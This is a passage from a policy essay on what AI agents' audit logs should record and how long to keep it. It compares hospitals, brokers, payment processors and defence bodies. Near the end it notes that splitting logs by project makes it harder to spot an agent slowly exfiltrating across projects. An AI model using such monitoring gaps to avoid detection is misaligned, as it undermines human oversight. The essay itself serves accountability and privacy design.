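| Full log, where the registry keeps a good log of its own | Nine times in ten, the registry's log yields the same 340 names | $5,000 | $7,500 | −$2,500 | 0.7% |

Keyed tokens do best. They cut the cost of theft, and they preserve the saving because the holder of the key can still name all 340 patients.

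Shorter retention is worse than a year's retention here because it saves $5,000 in expected theft costs but loses about $10,000 when a hijacking is discovered after the entries have been deleted. If the chance of theft were above 2%, shorter retention would be better. The hospital can get most of both benefits by deleting arguments and results after 90 days and keeping the patient tokens for a year, since the tokens are enough to identify whom to notify.

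The last variation is the strongest argument against capturing content. If another system already records which patients the agent looked up, a second copy adds little evidence but is just as attractive to attackers. Before the hospital starts logging the arguments of tool calls, it should find out what the registry's own log contains and how long the registry keeps it.

The calculation also leaves out several things, the largest of which is harm to patients. The expected number of patients in a stolen log is 1,500 a year (1% of 150,000), so the full log loses its $42,400 advantage if the theft harms each of them by more than about $28 on average. That is a low figure for the harm done when a stranger learns of a patient's cancer diagnosis. The calculation omits benefits of the log too. The log may help staff stop a hijacked agent early, and patients who learn promptly that they are among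 the 340 can protect themselves.

Fines can be larger than every figure in the table. Presence Health, a US hospital network, paid $475,000 in 2017 to settle a case about breach notices it sent more than a month late. The cost of stolen credentials is harder to estimate because, as at Cursor, they can give access to systems far beyond the log.

### Logging everything and logging little

Nian and colleagues make the fullest case for detailed records. They hold that nobody can hold an agent accountable without enough evidence to reconstruct what it did, and that "auditability is not a tax on agent development". They answer four objections:

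- To the view that ordinary monitoring tools are enough, they reply that a dashboard of prompts and tool names can still omit approvals, data categories and the identity of the caller.
- To the view that blocking bad calls matters more, they reply that a blocked call still needs an explanation and an allowed one still needs a trace.
- Some people expect better-behaved models to make records less important. Nian and colleagues reply that many failures come from changed tools, outside services and human approvals, which a better model doesn't fix.
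- To the objection that such records cost too much or invade privacy, they reply that organisations should design the evidence better, with selective recording, redaction, encryption and hashed summaries.

The last reply is a large concession, because someone who records selectively and redacts the rest is no longer logging everything. Nian and colleagues also acknowledge that detailed records can conflict with data minimisation under the GDPR, and that they have not established which privacy techniques preserve enough detail for an audit.

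FINRA comes closer to the maximal position when it suggests that brokers consider storing logs of prompts and outputs. The practical argument is that nobody knows in advance which field an investigation will need. Anthropic's full transcripts, for example, were useful months after its April incidents.

France's CNIL takes the opposite view and advises against copying a system's data into its logs. OpenTelemetry's defaults also keep this data out. The best evidence for this side is the Cursor theft, because if Cursor had deleted the 2025 traces, the attacker would have found no credentials in them. The maximalist can reply that without tool-call arguments in its log, the hospital could not have named its 340 patients. A defender of CNIL's advice can answer that logging a token for each patient would have been enough to identify them.

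An organisation can follow both Anthropic's and Cursor's examples by recording everything while it tests an agent on fictitious patients, and much less once the agent handles real ones. Anthropic's useful transcripts came from tests, in which few real people's data should appear, whereas Cursor's came from its users' work.

Some evidence points to both the value of a log and the risk of holding one. Nian and colleagues report that their scanner found 617 security problems in six well-known open-source agent projects and rated 44% of them critical. Most involved tools that accept the model's input without checking it. The researchers treat this as a sign that such systems aren't ready for an audit. Software with that many security problems is also a risky place to store patients' diagnoses.

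There is a strong case for recording facts about every call, but a weak one for keeping the text of every call. An organisation has good reason to keep the text when no other system holds it and the call sends something out or changes something. It has much less reason to copy what an agent only read.

Nian and colleagues also propose an "Auditability Card", a set of six disclosures about an agent system. Five cover their dimensions of auditability, and the sixth covers what happens if the log is missing. A hospital can ask a supplier for these disclosures before it buys an agent. It should also ask who can read the log and what a thief would learn from it, which the card doesn't cover.

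### When the model provider keeps nothing

A broker or hospital with a zero-retention contract may be legally required to keep, for years, some of the material that its model provider deletes. The contract and the legal requirement usually don't conflict, because the contract limits the provider's copies and the requirement applies to the customer. If a broker's agent emails a client, the provider can delete the text at once while the broker keeps the email in its own archive.

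The conflict arises when the provider holds the only record. This can happen with agents that run on the provider's servers, and with products whose audit exports depend on stored sessions. Anthropic's Compliance API, for example, omits sessions on users' machines under zero retention. A broker whose staff use an agent this way would get no transcript from the provider, so it would have to record the sessions itself, in its own harness or with OpenTelemetry.

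Existing recordkeeping duties generally cover an AI system's work, so a regulator is unlikely to excuse missing records because the provider deleted them. PYMNTS reports that enforcement has already begun without AI-specific rules.

Retention by the provider causes problems of its own. Thirty days is far too short for a broker's three-year duty and longer than a hospital may want an outside company to hold a diagnosis. The hospital also can't count on zero retention lasting, since a provider may withdraw it. Three measures reduce the dependence on such terms:

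1. The harness writes the hospital's own record before it sends anything to the provider, so that deletion elsewhere never destroys the only copy.
2. The harness replaces Mrs Keller's name and patient number with placeholders before the model reads them, then restores the real values when a tool needs them. The provider's copy then contains a diagnosis without a name, although rare details could still identify her.
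3. The contract requires notice before any change in retention, and staff treat a change of model as a change in who holds patient data.

Placeholders can make an agent less accurate, for instance when a task depends on telling two similar names apart, so the organisation needs to test them. If it expects a lawsuit, it has to suspend its own deletion schedule early, because it can't recover anything a zero-retention provider has already discarded.

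### Scanning the log for data that shouldn't be there

Most organisations apply data-loss prevention (DLP) to email, file transfers and laptops. The log needs it too, because its contents can leave the organisation through an export to a vendor, a support ticket or a developer's test case.

Scanning a full-text log for patient data works badly. If the hospital's agents make 10,000 calls a day and half of them return patient data, the scanner will correctly report patient data 5,000 times a day, and nobody will read the reports. Scanning works much better on the open half of a two-level store. The open record should contain only tokens and derived facts, so a patient number there means something has broken, perhaps because an update added a field or a developer turned on a debug setting. Staff can manage a handful of such alerts a week, and each points to a fault that someone can fix.

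Timing and location matter as well:

- *Before writing.* The harness scans the text before sealing it, and removes passwords and card security codes at this point.
- *At each exit.* A second scan covers anything on its way to the vendor, the SIEM or a support system. It blocks the transfer if it finds an identifier.
- *In storage.* A regular search of old open records, using newly written patterns, finds items that earlier scans missed.

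When a scan finds a working password, staff should change the password first and clean up the log afterwards.

A DLP product can also increase the risk of a leak, because many such products save the matched text as evidence for the analyst. That would create a ninth place from which Mrs Keller's diagnosis could leak. The hospital should set the product to save only the type of data, the entry's identifier and the field. Like a redactor, the product should run on the hospital's own machines.

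Even a well-placed scanner flags harmless data and misses sensitive data. It can use the check digit to reject invalid card numbers, but about one in ten random 16-digit numbers passes that test. A log with 10,000 such identifiers could therefore produce about 1,000 false matches, unless the scanner also checks for opening digits that card issuers use. Scanners can also miss paraphrased information, as in the AgentLeak tests, so a clean scan is weak evidence that a log contains no diagnoses.

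### Choices for four kinds of organisation

The arrangements below apply this reasoning to a hospital, a broker-dealer, a payment processor and a defence or intelligence body. They are starting points for a log of an agent's work with real people or operations. Retention periods not based on law are judgements that each organisation should adjust.

| | Hospital | Broker-dealer | Payment processor | Defence or intelligence body |
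|---|---|---|---|---|
| In clear | User, agent, tool, time, patient token, data class, recipient match, approval | User, agent and model version, tool, time, account token, order reference, approval | User, agent, tool, time, card token, amount, status, attempt number | User token, coded tool name, time, decision |
| Sealed | Text of emails and of changes to records | Prompts, advice, names and sizes of trades | Customers' messages and contact details | Arguments, results, errors, and the key to the coded names |
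| Left out | Results that the registry already holds | Market prices and archived emails, replaced by references | Security codes and full card numbers | Anything above the log's own classification |
| Host | The hospital; a vendor gets only timings and error counts | A regulated archive for business records; the firm's own servers for the rest | The processor, on servers apart from the payment system | The organisation's own network, at the level its contents require |
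| Retention | Open records 12 months; sealed records 90 days; facts about listed disclosures six years | Business records three or six years; the rest one year | Open records 12 months, the latest three at hand; sealed records six months | 30 months, unless the responsible authority sets another period |
| Who opens sealed records | The privacy officer, with a second person's approval | Compliance staff, and regulators on request | A disputes or fraud specialist, with a second person's approval | An investigator cleared for that project, with a security officer's approval |

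**The hospital** values its log mainly for showing whom to notify, so it keeps patient tokens for the whole year. For each registry query, it stores a reference to the record and its version instead of the result. An investigator can then look up what the agent saw if the registry keeps old versions. Otherwise, the hospital has to seal the result too, at least for calls that led to an email.

Emails are different because the agent writes them, and their wording shows what leaked. The hospital encrypts them to the standard HHS recognises, so that it doesn't have to notify patients if someone steals the sealed store without its key. Developers work with fictitious patient records and timings, and need a reason and approval to see anything else. If the agent becomes a high-risk system under the AI Act after December 2027, the hospital should extend the 90-day retention period to at least six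 months unless it has advice that the open record is enough.

**The broker-dealer** has less freedom because the rules on communications and orders already determine what it must keep. It copies those items into its archive as they arise. Prompts are harder to classify. A prompt that led to an order or recommendation should go into the archive with it, since the firm may have to show why it gave the advice. The firm can delete other prompts after a year if its lawyers agree they aren't business records.

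The log doesn't always need to copy the text an agent reads. PYMNTS reports that in Regulatory Notice 24-09, FINRA told firms to address data privacy, data integrity and the reliability of their models if they use generative AI to review staff's electronic correspondence. An agent that does this work reads emails the firm has already archived, so its log can hold message numbers instead of the messages.

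A broker's log also has a commercial value that a hospital's lacks, because anyone who saw that an agent was about to buy a large block of shares could buy first. The name and size of a trade therefore stay sealed from ordinary security analysts. The firm can't destroy an encryption key to get rid of a business record early, and it needs a spare copy of each key in case a regulator asks for a record after the usual key holder has left. If the firm is listed, it can use the open records to count the affected accounts and orders within hours, which helps it decide whether an incident is material.

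**The payment processor** has the best case for recording little. Its payment system already stores each transaction, so the log needs only an amount, a status and a reference to connect a tool call to the full record. It should also record attempt numbers in the clear, because a repeated call may have charged somebody twice. The processor keeps customers' messages sealed for six months. Cardholders commonly have about four months to dispute a charge, so this gives the processor time to respond.

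The payment processor also gains the most from removing data before the first write, because PCI DSS bans keeping card security codes. If the filter that removes the data fails, the safer choice is to store the call without its arguments and raise an alarm. The processor would lose some evidence about that call, but the payment system would still have a record of the transaction.

**The defence or intelligence body** can't use the hospital's calculation, because there is no figure like $5 per notice for the harm done when a stolen log reveals which submarines an agency can track. A missed intrusion could be just as serious, so the body has strong reasons both to record a great deal and to protect the log as carefully as the systems it covers. Keeping full contents is easier to justify than in the hospital, because intruders who want secrets may stay hidden for more than a year. The 30 months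 in the table comes from the total time that US civilian agencies must keep most categories of log.

The organisation can limit the damage from a theft by giving each project its own log, keys and coded tool names. Detection rules run inside each project and pass only alerts and counts to a central team, and no outside vendor receives any of it. Separating the logs makes it harder to notice an agent that takes a little from each of ten projects, since no single log would look unusual. A small group with clearance for all ten could search across them when an alert justifies it, with a record of every search. The people in that group would be the most valuable targets in the organisation, so someone outside the group should review their searches.
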